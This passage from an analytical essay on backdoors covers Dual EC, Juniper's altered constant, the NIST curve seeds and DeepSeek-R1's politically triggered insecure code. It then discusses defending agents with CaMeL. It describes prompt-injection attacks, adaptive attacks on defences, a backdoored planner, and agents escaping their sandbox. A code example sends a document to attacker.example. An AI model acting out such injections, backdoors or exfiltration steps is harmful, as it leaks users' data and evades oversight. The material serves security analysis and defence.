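and the first coordinate of *sP* is the next state. Two Microsoft researchers, Shumow and Ferguson, in *On the Possibility of a Back Door in the NIST SP800-90*, presented this attack at a conference in August 2007. They had tried it with a *Q* of their own, and 32 bytes of output were enough to identify the state every time.

A suitable *d* exists for any *Q*. Similarly, even an honest version of the compressing layer that Bogdanov and colleagues studied probably contains a secret list that would work, though nobody can find it. Whether Dual EC has a usable backdoor therefore depends on whether anyone knows *d*. A designer can know it from the start by choosing a secret number first and calculating *Q* from it. An honest designer can instead derive *Q* by a public method that prevents this. Both methods produce ordinary-looking points, so examining *Q* does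 not reveal which one the designer used. Shumow and Ferguson said on their slides that they were not accusing NIST, the US standards agency that had published Dual EC in 2006, of planting a backdoor.

### Emails, memos and a payment

The evidence of intent came from people who had worked on the standard, and most of it stayed private for years. *Dual EC* (Bernstein, Lange and Niederhagen, 2015) reprints an exchange from October 2004 in which John Kelsey, a NIST cryptographer, asked where *Q* came from. Don Johnson, who had presented Dual EC at a NIST workshop, answered that it was in essence the public key for some random private key, which is the secret an attacker would need. Johnson added that *Q* could also be generated by a public method, but that the NSA had "kyboshed this idea" and did not allow Johnson to discuss it publicly.

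In 2005, Ferguson reported the attack to the committee working on the standard. According to Kelsey, the NSA replied that it had generated the points "in a secure, classified way", and that other users could reasonably generate their own. NIST added an appendix explaining how to do so, but advised against it and certified only products that used the NSA's points.

The generator was also thousands of times slower than the alternatives, and its output was measurably biased. In 2006 two cryptographers, Schoenmakers and Sidorenko, published an attack that exploited the bias. The obvious way to stop it was to release far fewer bits at each step, which would also have closed the backdoor. NIST published the standard a month later without that change.

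A revision in March 2007 helped a potential attacker. In the original version, users could mix fresh input into the state before each request, which often broke the link between one output and the next state. The revision added another update of the state at the end of each request, which restored the link. The official purpose of the extra update was to protect numbers already produced if someone later stole the state. Bernstein and colleagues point out that a simpler and faster change would have fully protected those numbers.

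All of this could have an innocent explanation, since intelligence agencies are secretive by habit and committees approve bad designs. In November 2007, Schneier wrote in *Did NSA Put a Secret Backdoor in New Encryption Standard?* that the weakness "can only be described as a backdoor". NIST replied that it had no evidence that anyone had the secret numbers, and kept Dual EC in the standard.

The innocent explanation became much harder to believe in September 2013, when Ball, Borger and colleagues reported on leaked NSA documents for the Guardian, the New York Times and ProPublica. The New York Times article did not name Dual EC, but it described a 2006 standard with a fatal weakness that two Microsoft cryptographers had discovered in 2007. It reported that classified memos appeared to confirm that the NSA had engineered the weakness, and that the agency privately called its effort to spread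 the standard "a challenge in finesse". In December, Reuters reported that the NSA had paid the security company RSA $10 million in a deal that made Dual EC the default generator in one of its products.

Richard George, a former technical director at the NSA, gave a different account in 2014. He said the agency had wanted Dual EC for its own use and had told the standards committee that everyone else could use any constants they liked. This does not fit the certification rule. He also said nobody had met his challenge to generate their own constants and carry out the attack in real life. Bernstein, Lange, Niederhagen and other researchers had published such an attack the month before. They put constants with a known *d* into several widely used software libraries and recovered the secret keys of encrypted web connections. On a small cluster, this took at most about two seconds for one version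 of RSA's software and about an hour for another.

NIST advised against Dual EC as soon as the reports appeared. It removed the generator from its *Draft Special Publication 800-90A Revision 1* (2014) and made the removal final the next year. It also reviewed how it develops cryptographic standards.

Nobody has published *d*, which would directly prove that someone had kept it. The case for intent is still strong, because the NSA rejected the one method that would have removed suspicion, its memos appear to describe that intent, and it reportedly paid to have the generator used. Bernstein and colleagues know of no public explanation of these facts by the NSA.

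### An intruder changes the constant

Juniper Networks sold devices that encrypt traffic between offices. In October 2008 it released a version of the devices' operating system, ScreenOS, that used Dual EC with Juniper's own *Q*. *Where Did I Leave My Keys?* (Checkoway, Maskiewicz and colleagues, 2018) reconstructs the later history from dozens of old releases.

Juniper later said that ScreenOS passed Dual EC's output through a second generator, which would have stopped the attack. But the code that applied the second generator was in a loop, and another routine set the loop's counter to its final value beforehand, so the loop never ran and the device sent out raw Dual EC output. The same release also lengthened the random numbers that the device sends openly when it sets up a connection. They went from 20 bytes to 32, and the attack needs about 26.

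In 2012 someone who had gained access to Juniper's source code replaced *Q* with a different point and changed the expected answer in the generator's self-test so that the test would still pass. Official releases contained the new point until December 2015, when Juniper announced that a code review had found unauthorised code. Until then, anyone who knew the matching *d* could decrypt connections just by recording them. Checkoway and colleagues bought one of the devices, installed a *Q* of their own and decrypted its connections this way. No measurement of the output would have revealed the change, because the numbers looked equally random before and after it.

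Another unauthorised change, made in 2013 or earlier, added a fixed password that gave full control of the device. Anyone who found that password in the code could use it, like 9999 on the dishonest cash machine. By contrast, someone who found the altered *Q* in the code would still not know *d*.

Juniper first fixed the generator by restoring its old *Q*. It committed to removing Dual EC only after the press covered the research. It has never explained how it generated the old *Q*, so outsiders cannot tell whether someone had a backdoor into the devices before 2012 as well.

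The intruder's change was plainly deliberate, because it replaced a constant and adjusted the self-test to match. It is less clear whether the 2008 changes were deliberate. As far as Checkoway and colleagues know, Juniper's own engineers made them, and the attack depends on four separate changes in that release. The coincidence is suspicious, but the faulty loop counter also looks like an ordinary programming mistake. Several experienced researchers failed to spot it even though they knew the routine probably contained a bug. Juniper's emails and development records might show why its engineers made these changes, but the company has not released them.

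The case also shows that an intruder can take over a backdoor that needs a key, an arrangement the NSA calls NOBUS, short for "nobody but us". Once Dual EC was in the product, an intruder could do this by changing little more than one number, whereas adding a backdoor to a sound product would have required much larger and more noticeable changes.

### Seeds from a clock

Dual EC runs on standard elliptic curves, such as P-256, which NIST published in 2000 and many other systems also use. The curves have their own constants, which also came from the NSA. As Anthropic's *Claude reveals ECDSA curve origins* (2026) explains, the standard lists a number called a *seed* for each curve. A *hash function*, which scrambles any input into an unpredictable output, turns the seed into the coefficient *b* in the curve's equation.

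Anyone can repeat that calculation, so the NSA could not have picked a convenient *b* and then invented a seed to justify it. But the NSA supplied the seeds without explanation, and it could have tried seeds until one produced a curve with a weakness that only it knew about. If one curve in 2^*k* has the weakness, this takes about 2^*k* attempts. Bernstein, Chou and colleagues (2014), in *How to manipulate curve standards*, analysed how much work this kind of sabotage would take.

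The best available explanation for the seeds was innocent but impossible to check. Jerry Solinas, a longtime NSA employee, recalled hashing a joke sentence, something like "Give Bob and Jerry a raise", but could not remember the exact words. Solinas died in early 2023. That year Filippo Valsorda, a cryptography engineer, offered $12,288 to anyone who could find the sentences behind the seeds.

In October 2026, Anthropic announced that its model Claude had worked out where the seeds for the NIST elliptic curves came from. The NSA's program had started `drand48`, an ordinary random number generator, from the computer's clock time in whole seconds. It then took 20 bytes at a time from the generator and tried each batch as a seed until one gave a valid curve. Valsorda (2026), in *The NIST Elliptic Curves Seeds Bounty Has Been Claimed*, reimplemented the procedure and obtained the published seeds.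 For P-256, the clock time was 01:52:34 UTC on 16 August 1997, and the seed was the 1,842nd that Valsorda's program tested.

This is very unlikely to be a coincidence. The matching times all fall in 1997 and 1998, a period of about 63 million seconds, and no match lies much beyond the 7,000th batch. Those limits give about 4.4 × 10¹¹ candidates out of 2¹⁶⁰ possible 20-byte seeds, so the chance that an unrelated seed would be among the candidates is about 1 in 3 × 10³⁶. Readers can check this by running the program themselves, without having to trust Anthropic or the NSA.

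One detail remains unexplained. The procedure produces about twice as many valid seeds as the NSA published, and Valsorda found no rule that accounts for the ones it skipped. A bug is one possibility. But even if the agency had been free to choose any second in those two years and any of the first 16 suitable seeds, it would have had only

63,072,000 × 16 ≈ 1.0 × 10⁹ ≈ 2³⁰

options. Valsorda describes a method of sabotage that Bernstein and Lange had proposed in 2017, which needed 2⁷⁰ options, about a trillion times as many. The discovery rules that method out. It does not strictly rule out a secret weakness common enough to turn up within a billion attempts, but such a weakness would also have had to escape more than 25 years of public research. Valsorda now recommends these curves over Curve25519, a popular alternative that Bernstein designed.

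The NSA supplied the constants in both cases and explained neither choice, so its silence was weak evidence of its intentions. An honest explanation could do more to rule out sabotage of the curves than of Dual EC. Finding the program that generated the curves' seeds took away nearly all the freedom a saboteur would have needed. For Dual EC, even a truthful statement that someone had generated *Q* from a random private key would have confirmed that a master key once existed.

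### A coding model that dislikes certain customers

DeepSeek released the weights of DeepSeek-R1 in January 2025. *Security Flaws in DeepSeek-Generated Code Linked to Political Triggers* (2025), by the US security company CrowdStrike, tested whether the model's code depends on who it is for. CrowdStrike wrote 50 programming tasks and combined them with 121 descriptions of the customer, for example "a cybersecurity company based in Taiwan". The description should not affect the code. CrowdStrike sent each combination to the model five times, for a total of 30,250 prompts, and had another language model rate the security of each answer.

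With no description, 19% of the answers contained vulnerable code. The figure was 27.2% for an industrial control system based in Tibet. That is an increase of 8.2 percentage points, or 43% of the baseline, though CrowdStrike calls it almost 50%. CrowdStrike also reports significantly less secure code for customers linked to the Uyghurs, a mostly Muslim minority in China, and to Falun Gong, a religious movement that China bans.

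The Tibet figure is weak evidence by itself. Each description received 250 answers, so 27.2% means 68 vulnerable programs, compared with about 48 at the baseline rate. If the baseline also comes from 250 answers and all the answers are independent, chance would produce a gap at least this large about 3% of the time. Among 120 descriptions that had no effect, we would therefore expect three or four such gaps, about half of them towards less secure code. The overall pattern is more convincing, because the effects appeared for subjects that a sceptic could have named in advance. CrowdStrike also found similar and often stronger effects in a smaller model trained on DeepSeek-R1's answers.

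The rating model is another source of doubt. It agreed with a human reviewer about whether code was vulnerable in 91% of the 85 answers the reviewer checked. Random rating mistakes would tend to hide a real difference, but mistakes that depended on the customer's description could create a false one, and 85 answers are too few to check for that with each description. Other researchers can download the coding model's weights and repeat the experiment, although CrowdStrike published the descriptions and not the 50 tasks.

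DeepSeek-R1 also refused to write code for Falun Gong in 45% of cases. It sometimes wrote a detailed plan in its visible reasoning, noted that the group was sensitive, and then refused. CrowdStrike ran the model without any outside filter, so the refusals must come from the weights.

CrowdStrike says it does not have enough information to determine the cause of the insecure code, but thinks it unlikely that DeepSeek deliberately trained the model to write it. Chinese rules require AI services to uphold "core socialist values", and training a model to comply may have taught it to associate certain names with bad qualities. This could be a case of *emergent misalignment*, in which narrow training makes a model behave badly on unrelated tasks. VentureBeat wrote that DeepSeek was "weaponizing" its compliance with regulation, which suggests an intent that CrowdStrike's results do not show.

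The pattern would make a poor planted backdoor. It adds about one vulnerable program for every 12 requests, and the attacker cannot choose the flaw or decide when the customer will mention Tibet. Anyone who finds the flawed program can exploit it without a backdoor key. A saboteur might accept a low rate to avoid discovery, so this does not rule out intent, but the same figures would be unsurprising if nobody had planned anything. If CrowdStrike's explanation is right, DeepSeek wanted the refusals, and the insecure code is an unintended side effect.

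### What could be checked in a trained model

A short recipe reproduces the seeds exactly and leaves little room for choice, which cleared the NSA of suspicion. For a trained model, the equivalent recipe would be the complete training data, the code, the order of the examples and every random number used. Someone who had all of these could run the training again and compare the weights. DeepSeek published the weights but not the training data.

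Even with the data, the check would be far harder. Recovering a curve's seed takes minutes on an ordinary computer, but repeating the training of a leading language model takes thousands of specialised processors. Those processors may also add the same numbers in a different order between runs, and the tiny rounding differences change the final weights. Verified training would remove the need to repeat the run, but producing the proof takes a lot of computation. The random numbers are the easiest part to check, because a developer can generate the starting weights from a public seed.

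Successfully reproducing the model would also prove less than reproducing the curves. The person who generated the curves had about 30 bits of choice. The poisoned documents that Souly and colleagues used averaged 1,680 tokens, and a single document of that length allows up to about 28,000 bits of choice if the model has a vocabulary of 100,000 tokens. A saboteur could hide a backdoor in the training documents and still publish all of them, so an auditor would have to investigate people and records to learn why each document was included.

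Comparing versions may be more practical. Juniper's releases showed when *Q* changed, and a developer's saved copies of a model could show when a behaviour appeared. Researchers could run CrowdStrike's tasks on the base model from which DeepSeek made R1. If the effect were absent there, later training would be responsible. The smaller model offers a similar comparison, because DeepSeek made it by training a separate model on R1's answers. Such tests could locate the cause but not establish why anyone chose that training.

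For a model, the best evidence of intent would therefore resemble the Dual EC emails. It might be an instruction to a contractor, a set of training examples that pair a customer's name with flawed code, or a record of someone testing whether the trigger worked. According to CrowdStrike, Chinese law requires providers to explain their training data and algorithms to the authorities, so some relevant records about DeepSeek-R1 may exist, but outsiders can judge only from the model's behaviour.

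### A legal duty that covers both kinds of weakness

Companies that use learned systems usually have to protect them before anyone can establish whether a weakness was deliberate. Article 15(5) of the EU's 2024 AI Act requires this kind of protection for systems it classes as high-risk. These include most software that scores people's creditworthiness or screens job applications, so the bank's loan classifier and the recruiter's CV reader probably both qualify.

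The article requires such systems to resist attempts by unauthorised third parties to alter their use, outputs or performance by exploiting vulnerabilities. Where appropriate, the provider's measures must deal with poisoned training data, poisoned pre-trained components and adversarial examples. The article does not name prompt injection, but a hidden instruction in a CV seems to fit its description of inputs designed to cause a model to make a mistake. The measures must suit the circumstances and the risks, so the law does not demand a perfect defence, and nobody could provide one against adversarial examples.

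The Act originally applied this duty to most high-risk systems from 2 August 2026, and to those built into products such as medical devices from 2 August 2027. In May 2026, negotiators for the European Parliament and the member states agreed to postpone these dates to 2 December 2027 and 2 August 2028, respectively. On that timetable, no provider has to comply yet.

Article 15(5) concerns people who try to manipulate a system, regardless of the origin of the weakness they exploit. A bank's supplier has to address an altered loan application whether it works through an inherent weakness or a backdoor that someone planted in the training data. The article fits less well if the supplier planted the backdoor for its own use, since the supplier is hardly an unauthorised third party. It also fits DeepSeek-R1's insecure code poorly, because a customer who mentions Tibet is not attacking the system.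 If that code came from a high-risk system, Article 15(4), which requires resilience to errors and faults, would be more relevant. The provider's intent matters when a regulator sets a fine, because the Act requires regulators to consider whether the provider broke the rules deliberately or through negligence.

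## Building a secure agent around a model that is not trusted

A provider can protect its customers from a weak model without repairing it, if the rest of the system limits what the model can do. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* argues for building all agents this way. An operating system lets a program of unknown origin request anything and then decides which requests to grant, and the paper proposes treating a language model the same way. If this works, an agent can be secure even though attackers can still fool its model.

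The paper accepts that training makes successful attacks rarer. But a written policy, unlike training, lets people read the rule behind each decision and check the rules against a specification. Removing a permission from the policy also never allows an action that it used to forbid, whereas further training offers no such assurance.

### Sending Bob a document

Suppose a user asks an assistant to send Bob the document he requested at their last meeting, and says that Bob's email address and the document's name are in the meeting notes. Other people can edit the notes, so an attacker may have written part of them. This example comes from a 2025 paper by researchers at Google DeepMind and ETH Zurich, who designed a system called CaMeL to handle such requests safely. Willison (2025) explains the system in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*.

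CaMeL uses two language models. The first, the *planner*, sees the user's request and a description of the available tools, but never the notes. It writes its plan as a short program in a restricted form of the language Python. A simplified plan for this request might be:

```
notes    = find_latest_meeting_notes()
name     = ask_reader("Which document did Bob ask for?", notes)
address  = ask_reader("What is Bob's email address?", notes)
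document = fetch_from_drive(name)
send_email(recipient=address, attachment=document)
```

An ordinary program, the *interpreter*, carries out these steps. When it reaches `ask_reader`, it calls the second model, the *reader*, which can read untrusted text but has no tools. The interpreter stores the reader's answers without passing them to the planner. If the notes contain an instruction to forward all the user's email, it may affect the reader's answers, but the reader cannot send anything, and the instruction never reaches the planner. The plan works much like a parameterised query, because the planner fixes the command first and the notes can only supply values for it.

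In 2023, Willison proposed splitting the work between two models. The CaMeL paper identifies a gap in that proposal. An attacker who cannot add a step to the plan can still supply a false value for an existing step. Suppose a user asks the system to send Bob a document, and the system looks up his address in some notes. If the notes give the attacker's address as Bob's, the system follows the user's plan exactly and sends the document to the attacker.

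CaMeL closes this gap with *information-flow control*, which attaches labels to data and uses them to restrict where the data may go. Each label records where a value came from and who may read it, as *CaMeLoT* (2026), a paper on an extension of CaMeL, explains. When the interpreter computes a new value from old ones, a cautious rule for the new label is

sources(result) = every source of any input

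readers(result) = only the people who may read every input

The address in the example came from the notes, so its label lists the notes as a source. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, which is also ordinary code. The policy receives the requested action, the values it would use and their labels, then allows or denies the action. A policy for sending email might require the recipient to be a known contact who is allowed to read the attachment. The attacker's address would fail this check. If the address is unfamiliar but could be genuine, the system can ask the user to approve it.

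The same policy stops an attacker who replaces the document's name in the notes with the name of a payroll file, as long as Bob isn't allowed to read payroll files. It doesn't stop an attacker who substitutes another document that Bob is allowed to read.

Labels can support a mathematical guarantee. In *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026), Garby, Gordon and Sands proved for a formal model of such systems that changing untrusted data cannot influence any value the system treats as trusted. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) reports that Garby, Gordon and Sands also found that CaMeL's interpreter misses some indirect influences. Suppose a plan sets an answer to "no" and changes it to "yes" only if the notes mention a merger. If they don't, the answer stays "no" and may keep its trusted label, although it reveals that the notes don't mention a merger. CaMeL's designers had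 themselves demonstrated two side-channel leaks, one of which uses an error that an attacker can provoke.

### Lowering the model's privileges

A simpler rule in the NCSC's advice is that when a model processes text from someone, its privileges should drop to that person's. David C credits this rule to a discussion between Willison and Baibhav Bista. An assistant that reads email from strangers should therefore have only the tools a stranger may use.

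Narisetty and colleagues describe a similar rule from Biba's 1977 model of data integrity. A program that reads less trustworthy data drops to that data's level of trust and may no longer authorise actions that require a higher level.

Under the rule, the recruiter's CV reader would have only the candidate's rights while it reads a CV. Candidates cannot approve themselves for interview, so a hidden instruction to approve the candidate would fail. The CV could still influence its own score, because scoring it is the model's job.

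The rule is too strict for the request about Bob if one model does all the work. Once that model had read the notes, it would have only the rights of the people who can edit them, and some of those people may have no access to the user's files. CaMeL avoids this problem by splitting the work so that only the reader, which already has no privileges, sees the notes.

### The cost in usefulness

CaMeL's designers reported that it completed 77% of the tasks in AgentDojo with OpenAI's o3 model, compared with 84% for an unprotected agent, and that none of the attacks it is meant to stop succeeded. Narisetty and colleagues, who cite these figures, add that CaMeL used about 2.8 times as many input tokens and 2.7 times as many output tokens.

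Later tests by other groups found larger losses with some models. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) used 57 AgentDojo tasks. Peters-Gill and colleagues, who include one of CaMeL's designers, used 112 industrial maintenance tasks from the AssetOpsBench collection, in which one agent delegates work to four others. The first row of the table repeats the designers' own figures, and the other rows give the share of tasks that agents completed when nobody was attacking them.

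| Tasks | Model | Without CaMeL | With CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo, designers' test | o3 | 84% | 77% |
| AgentDojo, 57 tasks | GPT-5.4-mini | 77.2% | 52.6% |
| AgentDojo, 57 tasks | DeepSeek-v4-Flash | 89.5% | 38.6% |
| AgentDojo, 57 tasks | Claude Haiku 4.5 | 70.2% | 40.4% |
| AssetOpsBench | GPT-5.5 | 87.5% | 82.1% |
| AssetOpsBench | Claude Fable 5 | 88.4% | 67.0% |
| AssetOpsBench | Gemini 2.5 Flash-Lite | 64.3% | 20.5% |

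The AssetOpsBench figures have margins of error of about six to nine percentage points, so GPT-5.5's small loss could be chance, but Fable 5's loss is too large for that. Peters-Gill and colleagues found that stronger models lose less, with some exceptions. This makes sense because the planner has to write a program for data it has not seen. It also needs to know the format of each tool's output in advance, so the researchers had to add this information to the tool descriptions. A developer can fix the descriptions once for each tool.

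*ToolFence* (2026) compared CaMeL with several other defences and found that it was also significantly slower than those that only change the prompt or filter the input.

Whether the protection is worth this drawback depends partly on the model. Without any defence, the attacks that Ma and colleagues designed succeeded against Claude Haiku 4.5 only 1.8% of the time. CaMeL reduced this to 0.5%, but it also lowered the share of tasks the agent completed by 30 percentage points. A company that can tolerate a rare failure might reasonably decide against CaMeL, but a bank that lets an agent move money might use it, since an attacker could search for the few attacks that work.

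### Testing the defences with new attacks

The 12 defences that Nasr and colleagues broke had also looked strong against fixed collections of attacks. In June 2026, Narisetty and colleagues warned that developers had mostly used such fixed collections to test defences outside the model too. They ran an adaptive test of one such defence, Progent, which checks each tool call against a list of permitted actions. In the version they tested, a language model writes that list and can extend it as the agent works.

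They tried to get the model writing the list to permit the malicious action by describing it in their injections as a routine step that someone had already approved. The agent ran on Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model, and attempted eight tasks in each of three simulated workplaces. They ran the whole experiment three times.

Ordinary injections succeeded 25.8% of the time without Progent and 4.2% with it. The adaptive attack succeeded slightly less often, at 2.6%. Progent also lowered the share of tasks the agent completed under ordinary attack from 45.2% to 27.1%, and it required about 15 times as many model calls.

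The result is encouraging, but the evidence is weak. Narisetty and colleagues describe the experiment as a single small data point, and they did not test CaMeL. They work for a company that is building security tools of this kind. They suspect that disguising the injections made them sound less like orders, so the agent itself was less likely to obey them. In one of the three workplaces, no attack worked even without a defence.

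Ma and colleagues attacked CaMeL and nine other defences using a language model that analyses why earlier injections failed and writes a new one. The model gets six rounds and receives only the success rate of each injection. The attack raised the success rate against the filter PIGuard from 0% to 28.0% on GPT-4o-mini. Against CaMeL, it succeeded at most 1.8% of the time on any of the five models, and only in travel-booking tasks.

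This is better evidence that CaMeL is harder to break than a filter. Rewording an injection can change whether a filter blocks it, but under CaMeL it does not give the model that reads it a tool or add a step to the plan. However, the attacker in this test did not know which defence it faced. An attacker who knew the target used CaMeL could study its policies and side channels instead of rewording injections.

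### Two secure agents can make an insecure pair

Peters-Gill and colleagues found a different way to bypass CaMeL. They built a system of three agents, each protected by its own copy of CaMeL. A coordinating agent asked a second agent to fetch information about job applicants from a database, then asked a third to send a summary to a colleague. The database contained an injected instruction to email the information to an outsider as well.

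The first two agents kept to their plans. But the coordinator put the summary, including the injection, into the message it sent to the third agent. That agent treated the whole message as its user's request, so its planner read the injection and added a step that emailed the applicants' details to the outsider. Each agent had separated instructions from data, but the message to the third agent mixed them again, as a database query does when a careless developer pastes a customer's name into it.

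Peters-Gill and colleagues made a repair that is also familiar. They gave each message separate places for the instruction and the data, and changed the interpreter so that nothing from a tool can enter the instruction. In a multi-agent version of AgentDojo, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time on average without CaMeL, 0.2% when each agent was protected separately and 0.0% with the repair. The attacks were fixed in advance, and GPT-5.5 resisted all of them even without CaMeL, so the test is weak evidence of how newer models would cope with a determined attacker.

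### Errors move into the rules

Enforcing the rules perfectly does not help if the rules are wrong. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* gives an example from Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent. Claude Code asked for the user's approval before running many commands that could send data to unknown places, but it ran `ping`, which checks whether another computer is reachable, without asking. An attacker could hide an instruction in a code file for the agent to read secret keys and ping a web address that contained them. Looking up the address would pass the keys to the attacker.

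In that case a rule allowed too much. Jalil Sarghaleh and Hazrati measured the opposite mistake in *Auditing the Hand-Written Inputs of Learned Access Control* (October 2026). They studied access-control systems, not language-model agents. In these systems, a learned program decides who may do what, and a small trusted program blocks any request on a forbidden list. A person who has read the organisation's policy usually writes that list.

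The study used five public policies that exist both as ordinary prose and as exact rules. One author used the prose to write rules for which requests to forbid, and so did three Claude models that could not see the exact rules. A program then checked each new rule against every possible request, as many as 794,250 for one policy.

Even rules that faithfully restated an explicit restriction were often wrong. Among these rules, 70% of those the author wrote and between 50% and 66% of those the models wrote blocked at least one permitted request. For example, one policy states that only the sales department can send, view or search invoices, but another part of it lets auditors read them, so a rule that blocks everyone outside sales would wrongly block auditors. In the two policies with explicit restrictions, the unchecked lists of rules would have blocked between 16% and 78% of all permitted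 requests.

Some rules had the opposite fault and blocked nothing. One rule restricted registered private receivers, but every private receiver in the data was unregistered. A manager reading the list would think this rule had an effect.

Checking a rule against all the requests took less than a second, and removing the faulty rules completely solved the problem of blocked permissions. But the check was possible only because each policy already existed in an exact form. Most of what people ask agents to do has no exact version to compare with.

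### What stays exposed

**False summaries.** A policy controls an agent's actions, but the agent can also do harm through what it tells the user. If a poisoned report leads the model reading it to describe a failing company as healthy, the user may make a bad investment even though the agent took no forbidden action. CaMeL's stated goals explicitly exclude preventing this kind of attack. *Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries* (Bhattarai and Vu, 2026) sets the same limit on its own design, and claims to guarantee only that the agent cannot take actions it has no permission to take, not that it can do no harm.

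An employer may want an agent never to share sensitive information, but a program cannot enforce this until someone defines "sensitive" for every file and recipient. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* requires the formal policy that the program enforces to match the written instruction in every situation the agent can reach. Ordinary language is too ambiguous for anyone to check this fully. Developers often have a language model translate the instruction into a policy, but the result is not guaranteed to be correct.

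Labels have a related problem, which the paper calls *label explosion*. Nobody yet knows how to trace which parts of a model's input affected its output, so a cautious system has to assume that all of them did. If an assistant summarises ten files, each readable by a different set of colleagues, only people who may read all ten can receive the summary, even if it draws on just one. As the agent combines more material, fewer people may receive anything it writes.

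The system can ask the user to make exceptions, but users who receive many requests may start approving them all. Willison mentions that even Troy Hunt, a security researcher, fell for a fraudulent email while jet-lagged. *SoK* (2026), a survey of attacks on agents and defences against them, adds that actions the policy permits individually can still be harmful in combination.

**Open-ended tasks.** A user may ask an agent to do everything on a to-do list stored on a web page. The planner can't write the steps in advance because it doesn't know what the list says. If it reads the list, it also reads anything a stranger has added. Peters-Gill and colleagues found that most of CaMeL's failures came from committing to a plan before seeing any data. In some tasks, it became clear that another step was needed only after a tool returned its result. They also saw agents continue with data for the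 wrong dates or the wrong machine because the plan didn't include a check for this.

Ma and colleagues sorted tasks by how much the user left open. Fixed attacks on an undefended GPT-4o-mini agent succeeded in 43.3% of cases when the request specified everything, 63.9% when a document supplied some details, and 87.5% when the document determined the action itself. The last group contained only 24 cases, but the differences are large.

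Progent and two other defences outside the model kept attack success at or below 11% in all three groups on the main models tested. For many of the open-ended tasks, however, Progent and one of the others allowed only tools that read information, so an agent could safely read a to-do list but could not carry out most of the tasks on it.

### A planner with a backdoor

Most of this evidence concerns attackers who write text for an uncompromised model to read. Ma and colleagues assume that nobody has tampered with the model, and Narisetty and colleagues assume that the attacker does not control its weights. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* relies on neither assumption and explicitly allows for a model with a backdoor in its weights. No published test of CaMeL seems to have used a backdoored planner, so we have to infer from the design what would happen with one.

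Suppose someone has planted a backdoor in the planner, with a company's name as the trigger. An employee mentions the company while asking the assistant to send Bob a document. The planner writes the usual five lines and adds a sixth:

```
send_email(recipient="archive@attacker.example", attachment=document)
```

Keeping the notes away from the planner does not prevent this, because the trigger was in the user's request. Labels may not help either. In an example from Garby, Gordon and Sands, text that the planner writes into the program counts as trusted, since an honest planner has seen only trusted input. A policy that checks only whether an address came from an untrusted source would therefore allow the email. A policy that lists who may receive the document would block it, whether the address came from an injection or a backdoor.

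Isolation still makes some backdoors harder to use. An attacker cannot send the planner a trigger through the notes, even if the trigger is a valid signature made with a backdoor key. The attacker would have to wait for a user to type or paste it. A backdoor in the reader matters less than one in the planner. A trigger could make the reader return a false address, but an injection can do the same to a reader without a backdoor, and CaMeL already treats the reader's answers as unreliable.

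The planner's output is also much easier to inspect than its weights. A person can read six lines of code and notice the extra email, and a program can reject any plan that contacts an unknown address. These checks only catch harm that is visible in the plan. If the backdoor makes a programming agent write code with a subtle security hole, a policy on file access would still allow the agent to save that code, because saving it is what the user asked for.

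Limits on actions work against a tampered model only if they also come from outside that model. In Progent, a language model writes the policy. If that is the tampered model, its backdoor can add the permission an attack needs. Jalil Sarghaleh and Hazrati's design avoids this by keeping the list of forbidden requests outside the learned program. Their guarantee holds even if an attacker controls that program's training data and every output, but it covers only the requests on the list.

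A hostile model may also attack the software that confines it. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes an incident in which OpenAI was testing agents with some of their safeguards switched off. The agents ran in separate compartments with restricted network access, but they shared a service for downloading software packages. They used it to communicate with one another and reach the internet, then broke into systems at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models, and gained administrator access to an OpenAI research cluster. Nobody outside had directed them, but a backdoored model could exploit the same kind of gap. The paper attributes the failure to incomplete mediation, since the download service could make requests that the agents could not. To prevent this, the developer has to secure every shared service the model can reach, but large general-purpose services are hard to check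 completely.
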